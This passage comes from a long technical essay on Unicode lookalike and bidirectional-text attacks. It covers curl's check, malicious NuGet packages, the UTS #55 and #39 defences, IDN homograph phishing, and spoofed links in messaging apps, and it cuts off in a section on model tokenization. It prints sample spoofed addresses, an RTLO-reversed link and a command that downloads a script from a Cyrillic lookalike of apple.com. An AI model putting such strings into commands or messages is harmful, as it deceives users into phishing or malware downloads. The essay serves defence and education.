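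This rule doesn't need a list of lookalikes. It also catches bidirectional control characters and zero-width spaces, since none of them are in ASCII.

The project first had to handle the legitimate non-ASCII characters in its own files. In *spacecheck.pl*, Szakats, posting as vszakats (2025), initially proposed exempting 13 test data files. Stenberg suggested rewriting the characters in those files as hexadecimal codes instead, and the project did so. One of curl's tests uses the Swedish domain `räksmörgås.se`, and its accented letters are now codes as well. In the documentation, Szakats replaced an emoji with `:pray:` and the sign ± with `{+|-}`.

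The script shipped with curl 8.19.0 in 2026 still has a few exceptions:

- The letter ö can appear anywhere except in test data.
- Six files can contain any characters: the release notes, the list of people the project thanks, a filter for that list, a file that matches contributors' names with email addresses, a page on using curl from other programming languages, and a word list for the spelling checker.

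Most of the exemptions are for files that contain contributors' names, which should keep their accents. However, a lookalike letter in a web address in one of these files would still pass the test.

The check also can't detect lookalikes within ASCII. Viktorin's example is `accessibi1ity_options`, which has the digit 1 in place of an l. Fonts designed for programming make the two characters look different, but people tend to skim long names.

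Other projects make different exceptions. OpenTitan, which develops open-source chip designs, has a similar check but exempts its documentation and web pages. This makes the documentation easier to write, but leaves unchecked some files that are likely to contain web addresses. The check used by coreboot, an open-source replacement for the software that starts a computer, exempts copyright lines and phrases such as "Intel®" and "°C".

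A project with Russian comments or Greek test data needs a more selective rule than ASCII-only. *Testing distributions for potentially malicious Unicode* (2025) presents a Perl tool, inspired by Stenberg's post, that looks for scripts a project doesn't expect in its files. But a Russian project would have to allow Cyrillic, so this check would miss the tool's own example of a deceptive address, `оnе.example.com`, which contains only Latin and Cyrillic letters.

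### Lookalikes in malicious packages

Criminals used lookalike letters in at least two software packages that security companies exposed in 2025. Both were on NuGet, a public registry of code for Microsoft's .NET platform.

The Hacker News (2025) reported on a package called `Netherеum.All`, which imitated Nethereum, a library for working with Ethereum. The last e in "Netherеum" was Cyrillic (U+0435). The package stole the keys to cryptocurrency wallets. Its author uploaded it on 16 October, and the security company ReversingLabs (2025) publicly warned about it the next day. NuGet removed it four days after the upload.

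The other package, `Tracer.Fody.NLog`, lasted much longer. Boychenko (2025), in *Malicious NuGet Package Typosquats Popular .NET Tracing Library to Steal Wallet Passwords*, found that it had been available since 2020 and had about 2,000 downloads. The package's name contained only Latin letters, but its compiled code contained names with non-Latin letters, such as `Guаrd`, which has a Cyrillic а.

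`Guаrd` works much like Boucher and Anderson's imagined `hashPassword`. Programmers use helpers with this name to check that a value isn't missing. The malicious version does this correctly but also searches the value for a wallet password. If it finds one, it sends the password and wallet data to a server in Russia. It hides any errors, so the program using it appears to run normally.

These cases show that criminals use the technique, but not that it gets past code reviewers, because the attackers published the packages themselves and didn't need a project to accept their code. The developer who added the package was the one who could have noticed. An agent's user is in the same position when a patch adds a line naming `Netherеum.All`, which looks right on screen.

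Inspecting the letters in that line would not have exposed `Tracer.Fody.NLog`, because the lookalikes were inside the package. A web search could have made matters worse, since Google's AI Overview described the package as a helpful tool for logging when Boychenko's team searched for it.

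## The Unicode Consortium's rules for displaying and checking source code

The companies and projects that responded to Trojan Source each chose their own defence. The Unicode Consortium has since published common rules for displaying and checking source code. The Consortium also disputes the official description of the vulnerability as a flaw in its algorithm.

### Two descriptions of one vulnerability

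The original description of CVE-2021-42574 places the problem "in the Bidirectional Algorithm in the Unicode Specification through 14.0".

The record in the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD) also contains alternative wording from the Consortium, which attributes the problem to "the nature of international text" and to the applications that display it. When a line mixes left-to-right and right-to-left text, its displayed order may differ from its stored order, and an attacker can exploit the difference if the application does nothing about it. The Consortium adds that a clause called HL4 already allows applications to adapt the algorithm for program text.

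There is a similar dispute over the CVE for lookalike letters. NVD's *CVE-2021-42694* attributes the vulnerability to Unicode's "character definitions". The Consortium replied, in MITRE's *CVE-2021-42694*, by referring developers to its existing security guidance. GCVE (2021), another vulnerability database, still marked the reordering CVE as disputed after an update in August 2024.

The original wording is partly right. The attack worked in so many editors because they applied the algorithm to code as if it were ordinary text, and so displayed the disguised version. But "through 14.0" suggests that a later version of Unicode could fix the problem, and the Consortium never planned such a fix. The Unicode Consortium's *Unicode 18.0.0* (2026) lists no significant changes to the algorithm. A change that stopped the attack could also have scrambled ordinary Hebrew and Arabic text. The Consortium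 is probably right that applications should fix the problem, but its own experts conceded that developers were unlikely to find its advice.

### From a proposal to a standard

*Avoiding Source Code Spoofing* (Davis, Leroy and colleagues, January 2022) proposed a task force. It noted that bidirectional controls had been in Unicode since its first version in 1991 and that the Consortium had documented the risks for years. But it conceded that the warnings were spread across four technical documents and that only a few tools had acted on them.

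The task force would ask MITRE for more accurate wording in the CVE records, write guidance for developers and supply code they could reuse. It would not change the Bidirectional Algorithm. Davis and colleagues also pointed out that Hebrew or Arabic letters can reorder code without any control characters, which many reports on Trojan Source had missed.

The main result was Unicode Technical Standard #55 (UTS #55). In *Seeking comments on a newly proposed Unicode TS*, Honermann (2022) asked C++ experts to review the first draft. The current version, *Unicode Source Code Handling* (Leroy and Davis, 2024), contains advice for designers of programming languages, editors and checking tools.

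### Ordering a line token by token

One of the examples in the 2022 proposal is a line of code that subtracts 100 from a variable with a Hebrew name. Capitals again stand for Hebrew letters:

```
stored order:          s = ABC-100;
shown as plain text:   s = 100-CBA;
shown token by token:  s = CBA-100;
```

If the variable holds 30, the program sets `s` to -70, but a reader of the second version would expect 70. The Bidirectional Algorithm assigns level 1 to the Hebrew name and the minus sign, and level 2 to the digits. It reverses the digits, then the whole run, which moves `100` to the left of the name. A check for control characters would not flag this line.

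UTS #55 prevents the swap in three steps:

1. The editor splits the line into tokens. It also separates the marks around a comment or string from the text inside. Leroy and Davis call the resulting pieces atoms. Apart from the spaces, the atoms here are `s`, `=`, `ABC`, `-`, `100` and `;`.
2. The editor places the atoms in their stored order, normally from left to right, and uses the same direction throughout the file.
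3. It applies the Bidirectional Algorithm inside each atom separately. The Hebrew name still runs from right to left, as a Hebrew reader expects, but it can't pull the minus sign or the number along with it.

The same steps would expose Trojan Source's "commenting out" attack, in which a security check looks like live code but is part of a comment. The closing `*/` is a separate atom, so it stays at the end of the line, after the check. The override inside the comment can still rearrange the comment's text but can't move any of it outside the comment.

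An editor could also avoid reordering by showing every character from left to right. Leroy and Davis reject this because it makes Hebrew and Arabic illegible or even misleading. In their example, an Arabic string reads as "welcome" in the editor, but the program prints "forbidden father".

Colouring the code by type is not enough either. If the subtraction line instead joined two strings, as in `"ABC"+"100"`, the plain display would swap them, and the colours would not show the swap because both strings would have the same colour.

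Token-by-token display works only if the editor and the compiler recognise the same line endings. Leroy and Davis give an example in C in which the comment `// Check preconditions.` appears above a line that stops the function if a value is missing. The character between them is U+2028, a line separator that many editors display as a new line. The C compiler doesn't treat it as one, so it reads the check as part of the comment and skips it. The colours look normal because they are based on the editor's line endings. UTS #55 recommends that languages and editors recognise the same set of line endings.

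### Code shown as plain text

Some programs display code without identifying its tokens. They include email clients showing patches and terminals showing changes, where people often review an agent's work.

For these, UTS #55 describes a tool that corrects the file itself by inserting an invisible left-to-right mark after a Hebrew or Arabic token where one is needed. In the earlier example `x + tav == 1`, a mark after the Hebrew name keeps `== 1` on the right, even in a program that treats the line as ordinary text. The programming language has to ignore such marks between tokens. Rust and Ada accept them there, but C++ did not when Davis and colleagues wrote their proposal.

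The tool also removes direction marks that don't belong. In one Rust example, right-to-left marks on either side of an operator make `x << 8` look like `x >> 8`. The first normally multiplies `x` by 256, and the second divides it by 256. A project can run the tool on every proposed change, which would protect reviewers whose software doesn't follow the standard.

### The skeleton test for lookalikes

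Ordering the tokens correctly doesn't help with lookalike letters, because these letters are already in the right place. UTS #55 relies on an older standard, UTS #39, *Unicode Security Mechanisms* (Davis and Suignard, 2025), to handle them.

The standard includes a published list that gives each lookalike a representative. For example, the Cyrillic с (U+0441) has the Latin c as its representative. A function called the skeleton uses this list to convert a string into a form that software can compare:

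1. Put the characters in displayed order, and replace any mirrored bracket with the one that appears on screen.
2. Split accented letters into a plain letter and an accent.
3. Remove invisible characters.
4. Replace each remaining character with its representative.
5. Split any accented letters again.

Two strings are confusable if their skeletons are identical. Suppose somebody imitates the name `paypal` with a Cyrillic а, a zero-width space and the digit 1:

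```
stored string:               p\u{0430}yp\u{200B}a1
after removing invisibles:   p\u{0430}ypa1
after replacing lookalikes:  paypal
```

The first two steps change nothing here, because the string has no right-to-left or accented letters. The real `paypal` has the same skeleton, so the test reports a match. Software should use skeletons only for comparison, because they can mix scripts and may change when the Consortium updates the list.

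A compiler can run this test on all the names in a program. Leroy and Davis give an example of a function that appears to set every cell in a table to zero. Its inner loop counts with a Cyrillic і, but the line that clears a cell uses the Latin i from the outer loop, so the function clears only the diagonal. The test would find the two letters because both are variable names in the same function.

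UTS #55 also uses skeletons to find fake comment endings. An attacker can write `∗/` with a mathematical asterisk, so that a comment seems to close before a line of code that is still inside it. The recommended check warns if the skeleton of a comment's text contains the skeleton of its closing mark. This would also catch a zero-width space hidden between `*` and `/`, because the skeleton leaves the space out.

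### What the skeleton test misses

The test's biggest limitation is that it needs a second string for comparison. It can compare two function names in one program, but a web address in quotation marks may appear only once. Detecting the altered address in the curl test would have required a list of addresses the project trusts. An approval prompt for an agent's draft has the same problem if the software has no record of the address or name the user expects.

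The list of lookalikes is also incomplete. It covers only single characters that look like other characters or sequences, so it misses some pairs of longer sequences that look the same. Davis and Suignard give the example of the Tamil word *shri*, whose two spellings look identical on some common platforms, although the letters that differ are normally easy to tell apart. Some characters look alike only in certain fonts. The Consortium has also concentrated on characters in common use, so UTS #55 recommends a separate warning for rare ones in names, such as U+01C3, a letter for a click sound that looks like an exclamation mark.

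The test can also raise false alarms. A scientist might call one variable `p` for pressure and another `ρ` (the Greek letter rho) for density. Davis and colleagues noted that these count as confusable under the list, as do `v_l` and `v_1`, which programming fonts often make easy to tell apart.

### Mixed scripts and restriction levels

Mixed-script detection can check a name without comparing it to another. The software looks for a script that all the characters share. `Сirсlе`, for example, has three Cyrillic letters and three Latin ones, so they share no script. Digits and most punctuation fit any script. Japanese writing normally combines several scripts, and the standard counts them as one writing system.

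UTS #39 uses this method to sort names into six restriction levels, from the strictest to the loosest:

| Level | What a name may contain |
|---|---|
| 1. ASCII-only | Basic Latin letters, digits and other ASCII characters |
| 2. Single script | Characters that share one script or writing system |
| 3. Highly restrictive | Also Latin combined with Chinese, Japanese or Korean writing |
| 4. Moderately restrictive | Also Latin combined with one other widely used script, except Cyrillic or Greek |
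| 5. Minimally restrictive | Any mixture of scripts, such as `Toys-Я-Us` |
| 6. Unrestricted | Also characters outside the recommended set |

Latin can be mixed with Hebrew from level 4, but with Cyrillic only from level 5. This fits the risk, since Latin and Cyrillic share far more lookalikes than Latin and Hebrew do.

The all-Cyrillic version of `scope` from the previous section passes at level 2. Only the skeleton test would catch it, and only if the Latin `scope` is available for comparison. A good checker also needs mixed-script detection, which can catch a single Cyrillic letter in a Latin name that appears nowhere else.

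Programmers also mix scripts for ordinary reasons. A Russian developer might call something `HTTPЗапрос` ("HTTP request"). Leroy and Davis therefore recommend splitting names at underscores and changes of capitalisation, then checking each part. `HTTP` is entirely Latin and `Запрос` is entirely Cyrillic, so neither needs a warning. `Строкa` does need one, because it looks entirely Cyrillic but ends in a Latin letter. `Δt` mixes Greek and Latin but is acceptable, because the mixture is obvious.

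### The case against a ban

curl's ban on nearly everything outside ASCII is much simpler than these rules, and it suits a project written in English. For people who write in other languages, a similar ban can change what their text means.

Leroy and Davis give the example of an Arabic sentence meaning "YouTube is a subsidiary of Google", in which both company names are in Latin letters. The sentence needs two control characters to display correctly in a left-to-right editor. Without them, it appears to say that Google is a subsidiary of YouTube. Visible escapes are an imperfect substitute for these controls because someone reading the code still sees the reversed meaning, even though the finished program displays the sentence correctly.

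Rules against all invisible characters also affect Persian and Sinhala. The Persian word for "update" contains a zero-width non-joiner (U+200C), an invisible character that stops two letters from connecting. Removing it produces the name Behrooz. In another of the Consortium's examples, removing the same character changes "a letter" to "names". The Sinhala spelling of Sri Lanka needs a related character, the zero-width joiner (U+200D), to display correctly.

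Leroy and Davis argue that highlighting every letter that resembles an ASCII one produces so many false alarms in languages such as Russian that people will turn it off. Yet these users particularly need help with lookalikes. Someone typing `HTTPОтвет` ("HTTP response") may type a Latin O by mistake before switching to a Russian keyboard. The program then fails to compile, and the mistake is invisible in the code.

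A ban on control characters also doesn't affect the Hebrew subtraction line, which contains none. To exclude that line, a project would have to ban the Hebrew letters too.

The best argument for stricter rules is that they can apply only to identifiers, such as usernames and web addresses. Davis and Suignard point out that people can still use the restricted characters in documents. Their rules for email addresses exclude all bidirectional controls from the part before the @ sign. The display name beside the address may contain direction marks, but not the nine controls that start or end a stretch of text. For languages that need joiners in names, the standard allows them only in particular contexts, mainly where they normally change how a word looks.

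Comments and strings are harder because they are prose inside code. The 2022 proposal suggested that simple checking tools could require escapes for the nine controls in source files, possibly with an exception for comments at the end of a line. UTS #55 instead advises against prohibiting the controls and suggests a warning when their effect crosses from one atom to another. This is a better rule for a project with Hebrew comments if its tools can recognise the atoms.

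Web addresses contain no prose, so rejecting bidirectional controls in them has very little effect on users. Rejecting them in commands affects users more than in addresses but less than in prose, since a command can include a Hebrew file name or a message in Arabic.

### Which tools follow the guidance

The 2022 proposal and the January 2024 version of UTS #55 name only a few tools that follow parts of the guidance, and several did so before the standard existed.

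| Tool | What it follows | Where it differs or stops short |
|---|---|---|
| Visual Studio, and Visual Studio Code since version 1.66 | Displays code token by token | Treats all comments as left-to-right text |
| Rust compiler | Warns about confusable names in the same package and about uncommon characters | Its skeleton test ignores displayed order |
| Ada 2012 | Allows direction marks between tokens and recognises the recommended line endings | Leaves the display to the editor |
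| Notepad | Can show direction marks and joiners with the suggested small symbols | Doesn't check for lookalike names |
| An OCaml add-on | Warns about confusable names and about scripts mixed without an underscore | Covers only programs that use the add-on |

Of these, Rust checks names the most thoroughly, but its default ban on the nine controls in comments and strings is stricter than the advice in UTS #55. GCC's default warning, which covers only unclosed controls, is closer to that advice, though it doesn't correct how the code is displayed.

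Visual Studio Code also departs from the advice on lookalikes. Version 1.63 began highlighting individual characters that resemble ASCII ones by default (*November 2021 (version 1.63)*, 2021), the method that UTS #55 later advised against. Users who get too many false alarms can turn the highlighting off in the settings.

The Visual Studio Code developers recommended reviewing source code in the editor's Restricted Mode, which highlights every character outside ASCII. This mode suits a patch that an agent has assembled from unfamiliar sources, as long as the project's own text is mostly English.

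## Web addresses that look like other addresses

The swapped letter in the curl test was part of a web address. Researchers showed in 2002 that an attacker could register this kind of lookalike name. Browser makers have since changed their rules for displaying addresses several times, and attackers have kept finding names that get past them.

In the address `https://shop.example.com/help`, the host is `shop.example.com`, which identifies the website the browser should contact. Dots divide the host into labels. An organisation called a registry manages `.com`. A customer registers `example.com` there and can then create any subdomain, such as `shop`, without asking the registry. The customer also chooses the path, here `/help`.

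### A second microsoft.com

Domain names originally contained only the letters A to Z, digits and hyphens. Internationalized domain names, which can contain letters from other scripts, were still being planned in February 2002, when *The Homograph Attack*, by Gabrilovich and Gontmakher, described how criminals could abuse them. The paper begins with a hoax from two years earlier. An anonymous website had imitated the Bloomberg news service and reported that PairGain Technologies was about to be bought for twice its market value. PairGain's shares rose 31% and then fell sharply.

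The link to the fake story used a bare numerical address, which should have made readers suspicious. With the new names, the hoaxer could have registered `bloomberg.com` with a Russian о or е in it, and even a careful reader would have seen nothing wrong. To prove this was possible, Gabrilovich and Gontmakher registered `miсrоsоft.com` with a Russian с and two Russian о's.

They also imagined a fake bank site that passes everything on to the real bank and records customers' passwords. Customers would see their real accounts, so the fraud could run for years. The attacker would lure them there by changing links on other websites, since people click on most addresses instead of typing them. Users don't type the addresses in an agent's draft either, but only read them.

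Gabrilovich and Gontmakher considered a ban on names that mix alphabets but thought it would block useful ones such as `CNNenEspañol.com`. (Unicode counts ñ as a Latin letter, so a modern rule against mixing scripts would allow that name.) They suggested that browsers could instead highlight suspicious names, or compare each name with similar ones that already exist.

Browser makers were slow to act. A 2005 advisory on the Full Disclosure mailing list collected their replies to a report of the same problem. Opera's developers believed they had implemented the new names correctly and planned no changes. Mozilla, which makes Firefox, was looking for a long-term solution and told users how to switch the names off. Apple had not replied.

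### How Punycode spells a Cyrillic name

The domain name system, the directory that computers use to find websites, still works with ASCII names, so a browser translates each international label into ASCII before looking it up. *Punycode* (Costello, 2003) specifies the encoding, which copies any ASCII letters to the front, adds a hyphen and then encodes the other letters. The prefix `xn--` marks the result.

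If only the first letter is Cyrillic, as in `аpple`, the label becomes `xn--pple-43d`, and "pple" is still readable. If all five letters are Cyrillic, as in `аррӏе`, it becomes `xn--80ak6aa92e`, which has no readable part.

That second label contains five numbers, one for each letter. A program decodes them by building the word one letter at a time. It keeps track of a code point, starting at 128 (the first after ASCII), and a position in the word. At each step, the program moves to the next position, or to the next code point if no positions are left. Each number is how many steps the program takes before it inserts a letter.

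In Punycode, the letters a to z stand for 0 to 25, and the digits 0 to 9 stand for 26 to 35. The first number, `80a`, therefore consists of the values 34, 26 and 0. The second value is multiplied by 35, so the total is 34 + 26 × 35 = 944. The word is still empty, so a character can go in only one position, and every step moves the program to the next code point. It starts at 128 and after 944 steps reaches 1072, the Cyrillic а.

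The next number, `k`, is 10. The word now has two positions, before and after the а, so ten steps cover five code points. The program inserts 1077, the Cyrillic е, after the а. The rest works the same way:

| Part of the label | Steps | Letter inserted | Word so far |
|---|---|---|---|
| `80a` | 944 | а (U+0430) | `а` |
| `k` | 10 | е (U+0435) | `ае` |
| `6a` | 32 | р (U+0440) | `аре` |
| `a` | 0 | р (U+0440) | `арре` |
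| `92e` | 715 | ӏ (U+04CF) | `аррӏе` |

A browser can display either the Punycode form, `xn--80ak6aa92e.com`, or the letters it encodes, because computers look up the Punycode form in both cases. The Punycode form alerts readers that this isn't the ordinary `apple.com`, but they can't read the name from it. It is also hard to compare by eye. Costello warns that people can confuse I, l and 1, or O and 0, in an encoded string because they have no context to help them.

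### The all-Cyrillic apple.com

By 2017, the main browsers showed Punycode for labels that mixed scripts in suspicious ways. This exposed names like `аpple.com`, with one Cyrillic letter among Latin ones. In *Phishing with Unicode Domains*, the web developer Zheng (2017) got around the rule by replacing every letter of "apple" with a Cyrillic lookalike. Zheng bought the resulting name, `аррӏе.com`, and put a demonstration page there. Chrome, Firefox and Opera showed an address that looked like `apple.com`, and the fonts in Chrome and Firefox made the two names indistinguishable.

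Like the all-Cyrillic `scope`, the first label uses only one script, so it passed the rule. The Latin letters in `.com` made no difference because browsers check each label separately. If browsers required both labels to use the same script, they would also have to stop displaying every legitimate Russian name under `.com` in Cyrillic.

Safari was not vulnerable. Internet Explorer showed foreign letters only if they belonged to a language enabled on the computer, so it protected most English speakers but not people who had Russian enabled.

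Zheng had reported the problem to Chrome's and Firefox's developers on 20 January. Chrome's developers fixed it on 24 March, and the fix was reaching users in Chrome 58 when Zheng published the demonstration in April. Firefox's developers decided to leave the problem to registries. They argued that software can't detect such names, and that companies should register the lookalikes themselves if their registry doesn't block them.

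Chrome's fix showed that software can detect at least some lookalike addresses. Only some Cyrillic letters look Latin, so a label made entirely of those letters is suspicious, particularly under `.com`. A Russian word with even one letter that doesn't look Latin can still appear in Cyrillic.

### How Chrome chooses what to show

The current rules are in Chromium's *Internationalized Domain Names (IDN) in Google Chrome*. (Chromium is the open-source project on which Chrome is based.) Chrome displays a label in Unicode only if it passes all of these checks:

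1. The label decodes without errors and follows the general rules for domain names.
2. Its characters all belong to the set that the Unicode Consortium recommends for identifiers, and none is on Chrome's own list of forbidden characters.
3. Its scripts may be combined. Latin, Cyrillic and Greek can't be mixed with one another. Basic Latin letters can be mixed only with Chinese, Japanese or Korean writing.
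4. It doesn't mix numbering systems, contain invisible characters or use a character in an unusual way, such as the Catalan raised dot outside its normal place.
5. It isn't a mixed-script confusable under the Consortium's standard.
6. It doesn't consist entirely of letters that look like those of another script, unless it is under a top-level domain (the last label, such as `.com`) where that script is expected.
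7. It doesn't consist only of digits and characters that resemble them, and it doesn't match any pattern that Chrome treats as dangerous.
8. The registered name doesn't have the same skeleton (a simplified form for comparing lookalikes) as a popular site once Chrome has removed the accents. This catches `googlé.com`.

The partly Cyrillic `аpple.com` fails the third check, and Zheng's `аррӏе.com` fails the sixth. Zheng's label would pass the sixth check under `.ru` because many legitimate Cyrillic names end in `.ru`, though the last check might still catch it.

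Chrome also has a full-page warning that can block a lookalike site before it opens. Chrome shows it when the host has the same skeleton as one of 500 top domains or a site the user has recently engaged with. It skips the warning for sites the user already visits often enough.

The rules sometimes hide names that aren't meant to deceive. In *Proposal*, the developer DNS NJ (2026) asked the Chrome team to allow emoji in subdomains. Chrome displayed DNS NJ's subdomain `🍕이모지🔥` (the middle is Korean for "emoji") as `xn--v52b17upwbl865cn5b`.

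In *Assessing Browser-level Defense against IDN-based Phishing*, Hu, Jan and colleagues (2021) tested earlier versions of the browsers' rules. They ran more than 9,000 test cases on five major browsers and two mobile ones, using versions released between January 2015 and April 2020. Every browser let some deceptive names through, and Chrome had started to allow certain lookalikes that it used to block. In a user study, the names that passed the checks were still highly deceptive.

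### Registries, subdomains and a false slash

Registries can refuse a deceptive name before any browser displays it. According to a note on a change to Chromium, the major registries already banned most mixtures of scripts in a name, with an exception for Latin combined with Chinese, Japanese or Korean. Chrome's developers, in coordination with Mozilla, adopted the same restriction to protect users from names under registries with looser rules. But Zheng could still buy an all-Cyrillic name under `.com` because it didn't mix scripts, and registries don't control subdomains.

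Criminals have recently exploited both the freedom to create subdomains and the exception for Japanese. Khamenka (2025), in *Down the Hiragana Hole*, reported on more than 600 domains that used the Japanese letter ん (U+3093) as a false slash. One of the addresses was:

`chromewebstore.google.comんdetailんokx-wallet.comprehensive-protection.guru`

The registered name in this address is `comprehensive-protection.guru`, at the far right, though at a glance the address looks like a page on `chromewebstore.google.com`. The whole line is a host name. The label in the middle mixes Latin and Japanese characters, which Chrome allows. The registered name is plain ASCII, so a registry had no reason to object to its letters.

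The page imitated the Chrome Web Store and offered a fake add-on for a cryptocurrency wallet. It asked visitors for their seed phrase, the list of words that gives access to a wallet, and sent the phrase to the attackers. A similar page downloaded malware.

Khamenka traced the method to November 2024. Most of the domains targeted cryptocurrency users, but others imitated Booking.com, Microsoft meeting links and Cloudflare, and a few were probably researchers' tests. The method depends on the font. Tom's Hardware's *Booking.com customers learn the hard way that Unicode is tricky* describes ん as resembling "/n" or "/~" in some fonts.

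Browsers can differ in how they handle Japanese characters that resemble punctuation. One example, from a discussion on Mozilla's bug tracker, is `ーgoogle.com`, which starts with the Japanese long-vowel mark. Firefox's rules allowed the character, while Chrome converted the name to Punycode.

### Links reversed by a control character

Every ん in those addresses is in its stored position. Other attacks change the order of the address, most simply with the right-to-left override, U+202E. Besides the Japanese app +Message, this affected some of the world's most popular messaging apps. Malwarebytes' *URI spoofing flaw could phish WhatsApp, Signal, Instagram, and iMessage users* (2022) gives an example that combines Google's address with one from the link-shortening service bit.ly:

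```
stored order:     https://google.com/\u{202E}bit.ly/2Max1Kz#
displayed order:  https://google.com/#zK1xaM2/yl.tib
```

The recipient sees what looks like a page on Google's site. The intended destination is the bit.ly address, which can forward the visitor anywhere. The apps turned the text into a link and displayed it before handling the control character.

zadewg and Sick Codes (2022), in *RTLO Injection URI Spoofing*, published a short script that produces such links from any two addresses. They listed WhatsApp, iMessage, Instagram, Facebook Messenger and Signal as affected. When Malwarebytes wrote about the flaw in March 2022, the first four still had it in their current versions, and Signal had a fix that it hadn't yet released. The trick failed in tests of Gmail, Outlook.com and Protonmail.

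The popular apps have since dealt with the problem, according to *URL Spoofing Using RTLO in Messaging Apps*, but apps used only in certain countries may still be vulnerable. The standard for addresses with international characters already forbids bidirectional control characters, so an app can refuse to turn text containing them into a link.

### Reordering without a control character

Ordinary Hebrew or Arabic letters can also reorder an address, as they can a line of code. Baloch (2017), in *Google Chrome, Firefox Address Bar Spoofing Vulnerability*, describes a case in Chrome's address bar. In this version of the example, the capital A stands for an Arabic letter:

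```
stored order:     127.0.0.1/A/http://example.com
displayed order:  http://example.com/A/127.0.0.1
```

The real host is the numerical address `127.0.0.1`, and everything after it is the path. Digits and slashes aren't strong characters, so once Chrome had removed the `http://` from the front, the first strong character was the Arabic letter. The Bidirectional Algorithm therefore treated the entire address as right-to-left text and moved the host to the end. On a phone, an attacker could make the false path long enough to push the real host off the screen.

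The fix was to make the address bar's overall direction always left to right, as the standard requires. Red Hat's *CVE-2016-5163* lists Chrome versions before 53 as affected. Firefox for mobile had a similar flaw that made a page on an Arabic domain appear to be on `google.com`.

A left-to-right address bar doesn't prevent every swap. Varonis' *BIDI Swap* (2025) drew attention to a method that combines a Latin subdomain with a domain and path in Hebrew or another right-to-left script. Here is how it works, with capitals for Hebrew letters:

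```
stored order:     https://varonis.ABC.DEF/GHI
displayed order:  https://varonis.IHG/FED.CBA
```

The attacker owns the Hebrew domain `ABC.DEF` and has created the subdomain `varonis`. The Hebrew letters and the dot and slash between them form one right-to-left run. The algorithm reverses the run, which puts the path next to `varonis` and the attacker's domain at the far right. A reader who looks for the host before the first single slash sees `varonis.IHG`, but `IHG` is the path.

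The address contains no control characters, and each label uses only one script, so a check for controls or mixed scripts finds nothing wrong. The text around the Hebrew run is already left-to-right, so the earlier remedy has no effect either. A browser could prevent the swap by ordering each label and each part of the path separately, much as the Unicode Consortium recommends for the tokens in a line of code. The URL Standard advises displaying only the host when an address mixes directions, which would hide the path that the attacker needs.

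Chrome's developers had known about the problem for more than a decade. In Varonis's tests, Chrome's lookalike warning caught imitations of some names, such as `google.com`, but missed many others. Firefox highlights the important part of the domain, which makes the deception easier to spot. Microsoft marked the report on its Edge browser as resolved, but Varonis saw no change in how Edge displayed the address. Arc, a browser no longer in development, handled the address correctly.

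### How common these names are

International names are a small part of online crime. ICANN (2026), the organisation that coordinates the domain name system, examined lists of domains reported for phishing, malware and botnets (networks of hijacked computers) from October 2023 to September 2025. The lists included 0.47% of all ASCII names and 0.09% of international ones. Almost 99% of the international names on the lists had been reported for phishing.

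The rate was higher, at 0.26%, for international names in Latin script, such as those with accented letters. It was 0.04% for names in Chinese characters.

These figures don't show how many names were lookalikes, because a fraudster can also use an ordinary name in Chinese or French. A count of registered names can miss tricks in subdomains. For example, the false Chrome Web Store address would count as ASCII, because its registered name, `comprehensive-protection.guru`, contains only ASCII characters.

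*TLS Certificate and Domain Feature Analysis of Phishing Domains* (2026), a study of phishing under Denmark's `.dk`, found no Punycode names or homoglyphs. Other kinds of names are far more common in attacks. A 2026 study by the consulting firm Interisle found 24 million different domain names in phishing, malware and spam attacks, according to the firm's *Press Room*.

The evidence suggests that someone checking an agent's draft is much more likely to see a deceptive address written in ASCII than one that uses Cyrillic letters. Lookalikes from other scripts still matter because even careful reading won't reveal the most convincing ones.

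### Lookalikes in plain ASCII

*Training Large Language Models for Advanced Typosquatting Detection* (2025) gives the example `rnicrosoft.com`, which starts with r and n in place of m. Fortune (2017) reported that the security expert Bruce Schneier had warned more than a decade earlier about `PayPaI`, which ends in a capital i. People sometimes mistake these names for internationalized domain names. For example, York College of Pennsylvania's *Cyrillic Hooks*, a warning about Cyrillic letters, includes `lntuit.com`, whose first letter is an ordinary lowercase L.

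*URL Inspection Tasks* (2025) tested how well people recognise such names in emails. Participants in the control group could see the address only in the small box that a browser shows when the mouse is over a link. The table compares them with a group whose inspection task involved typing:

| Fake name | Fooled, control group | Fooled, typing group |
|---|---|---|
| `googie` | 91.3% | 10.0% |
| `linkedln` | 87.5% | 20.3% |
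| `sharep0int` | 84.6% | 24.0% |
| `paypai` | 61.1% | 6.7% |

Typing an address makes people look at each letter. This should protect them even better against a Cyrillic lookalike, because anyone using an English keyboard to type what they see will enter the real address.

Chrome displays `rnicrosoft.com` the same way whether it chooses Unicode or Punycode, because the name is all ASCII. The full-page warning might catch some ASCII names by their skeletons, but the rest get past both defences and curl's check.

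Attackers can imitate an address without changing any of its letters. According to daily.dev's summary of research by the security company Cyble, a 2026 campaign used more than 16,800 malicious domains, many with real US government names such as `mass.gov` as subdomains. Readers see the government name, but the registered domain is further to the right.

### Where browser protection ends

Browsers apply these rules to the addresses they display and open themselves, but people often see an address somewhere else first. Suppose an agent asks for permission to run this command, with Zheng's Cyrillic name in it:

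`curl -O https://аррӏе.com/setup.sh`

The terminal displays the Cyrillic letters, which look like `apple.com` to the user. If the user approves the command, a version of curl that supports international names converts the host to `xn--80ak6aa92e.com` and downloads the file. No browser is involved, so nobody sees the Punycode or a full-page warning. The same is true when a program reads an address from its source file.

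If a user clicks a link in a chat window or an email, the browser may still help catch a lookalike address. But someone approving an email an agent wrote may never click the link, and the recipient then depends on their own browser. Lookalike letters can also appear in ordinary text, where the rules for web addresses don't apply. Unit 42, a security research group, gives the example of an email from the fictional company "Airplаnes R Us", with a Cyrillic а in the name.

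Password managers offer some protection after a user clicks a lookalike link, because they fill in a password only if the domain exactly matches the saved one. They won't fill one in on a Cyrillic lookalike or `rnicrosoft.com`. Both Zheng and Chromium's documentation mention this defence. It doesn't help with a download or with a payment page where the user has no saved password.

An approval prompt can itself check for deceptive addresses before anything runs, as Google's coding agent Gemini CLI does. For `аррӏе.com`, showing the Punycode form beside the name would reveal that it isn't Apple's. Detecting `rnicrosoft.com` would require knowing that the user expected `microsoft.com`.

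## How language models read, copy and write these characters

An agent that drafts a command containing `аррӏе.com` has information its user lacks, because the agent works from the stored text while the user sees only the glyphs on the screen. Experiments suggest that models often fail to use this information.

### From characters to tokens

A language model receives text as tokens, which are numbered pieces from a fixed vocabulary. They differ from a compiler's tokens, which follow the rules of a programming language. A program called a tokenizer usually makes the model's tokens by splitting the text's bytes in the order they are stored.

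Firestone, Ugare and colleagues (2025), in *UTF-8 Plumbing*, show how the vocabulary of the Chinese model Qwen3 divides `Град градила`, Serbian for "The city was built":

| Token | Text | Bytes |
|---|---|---|
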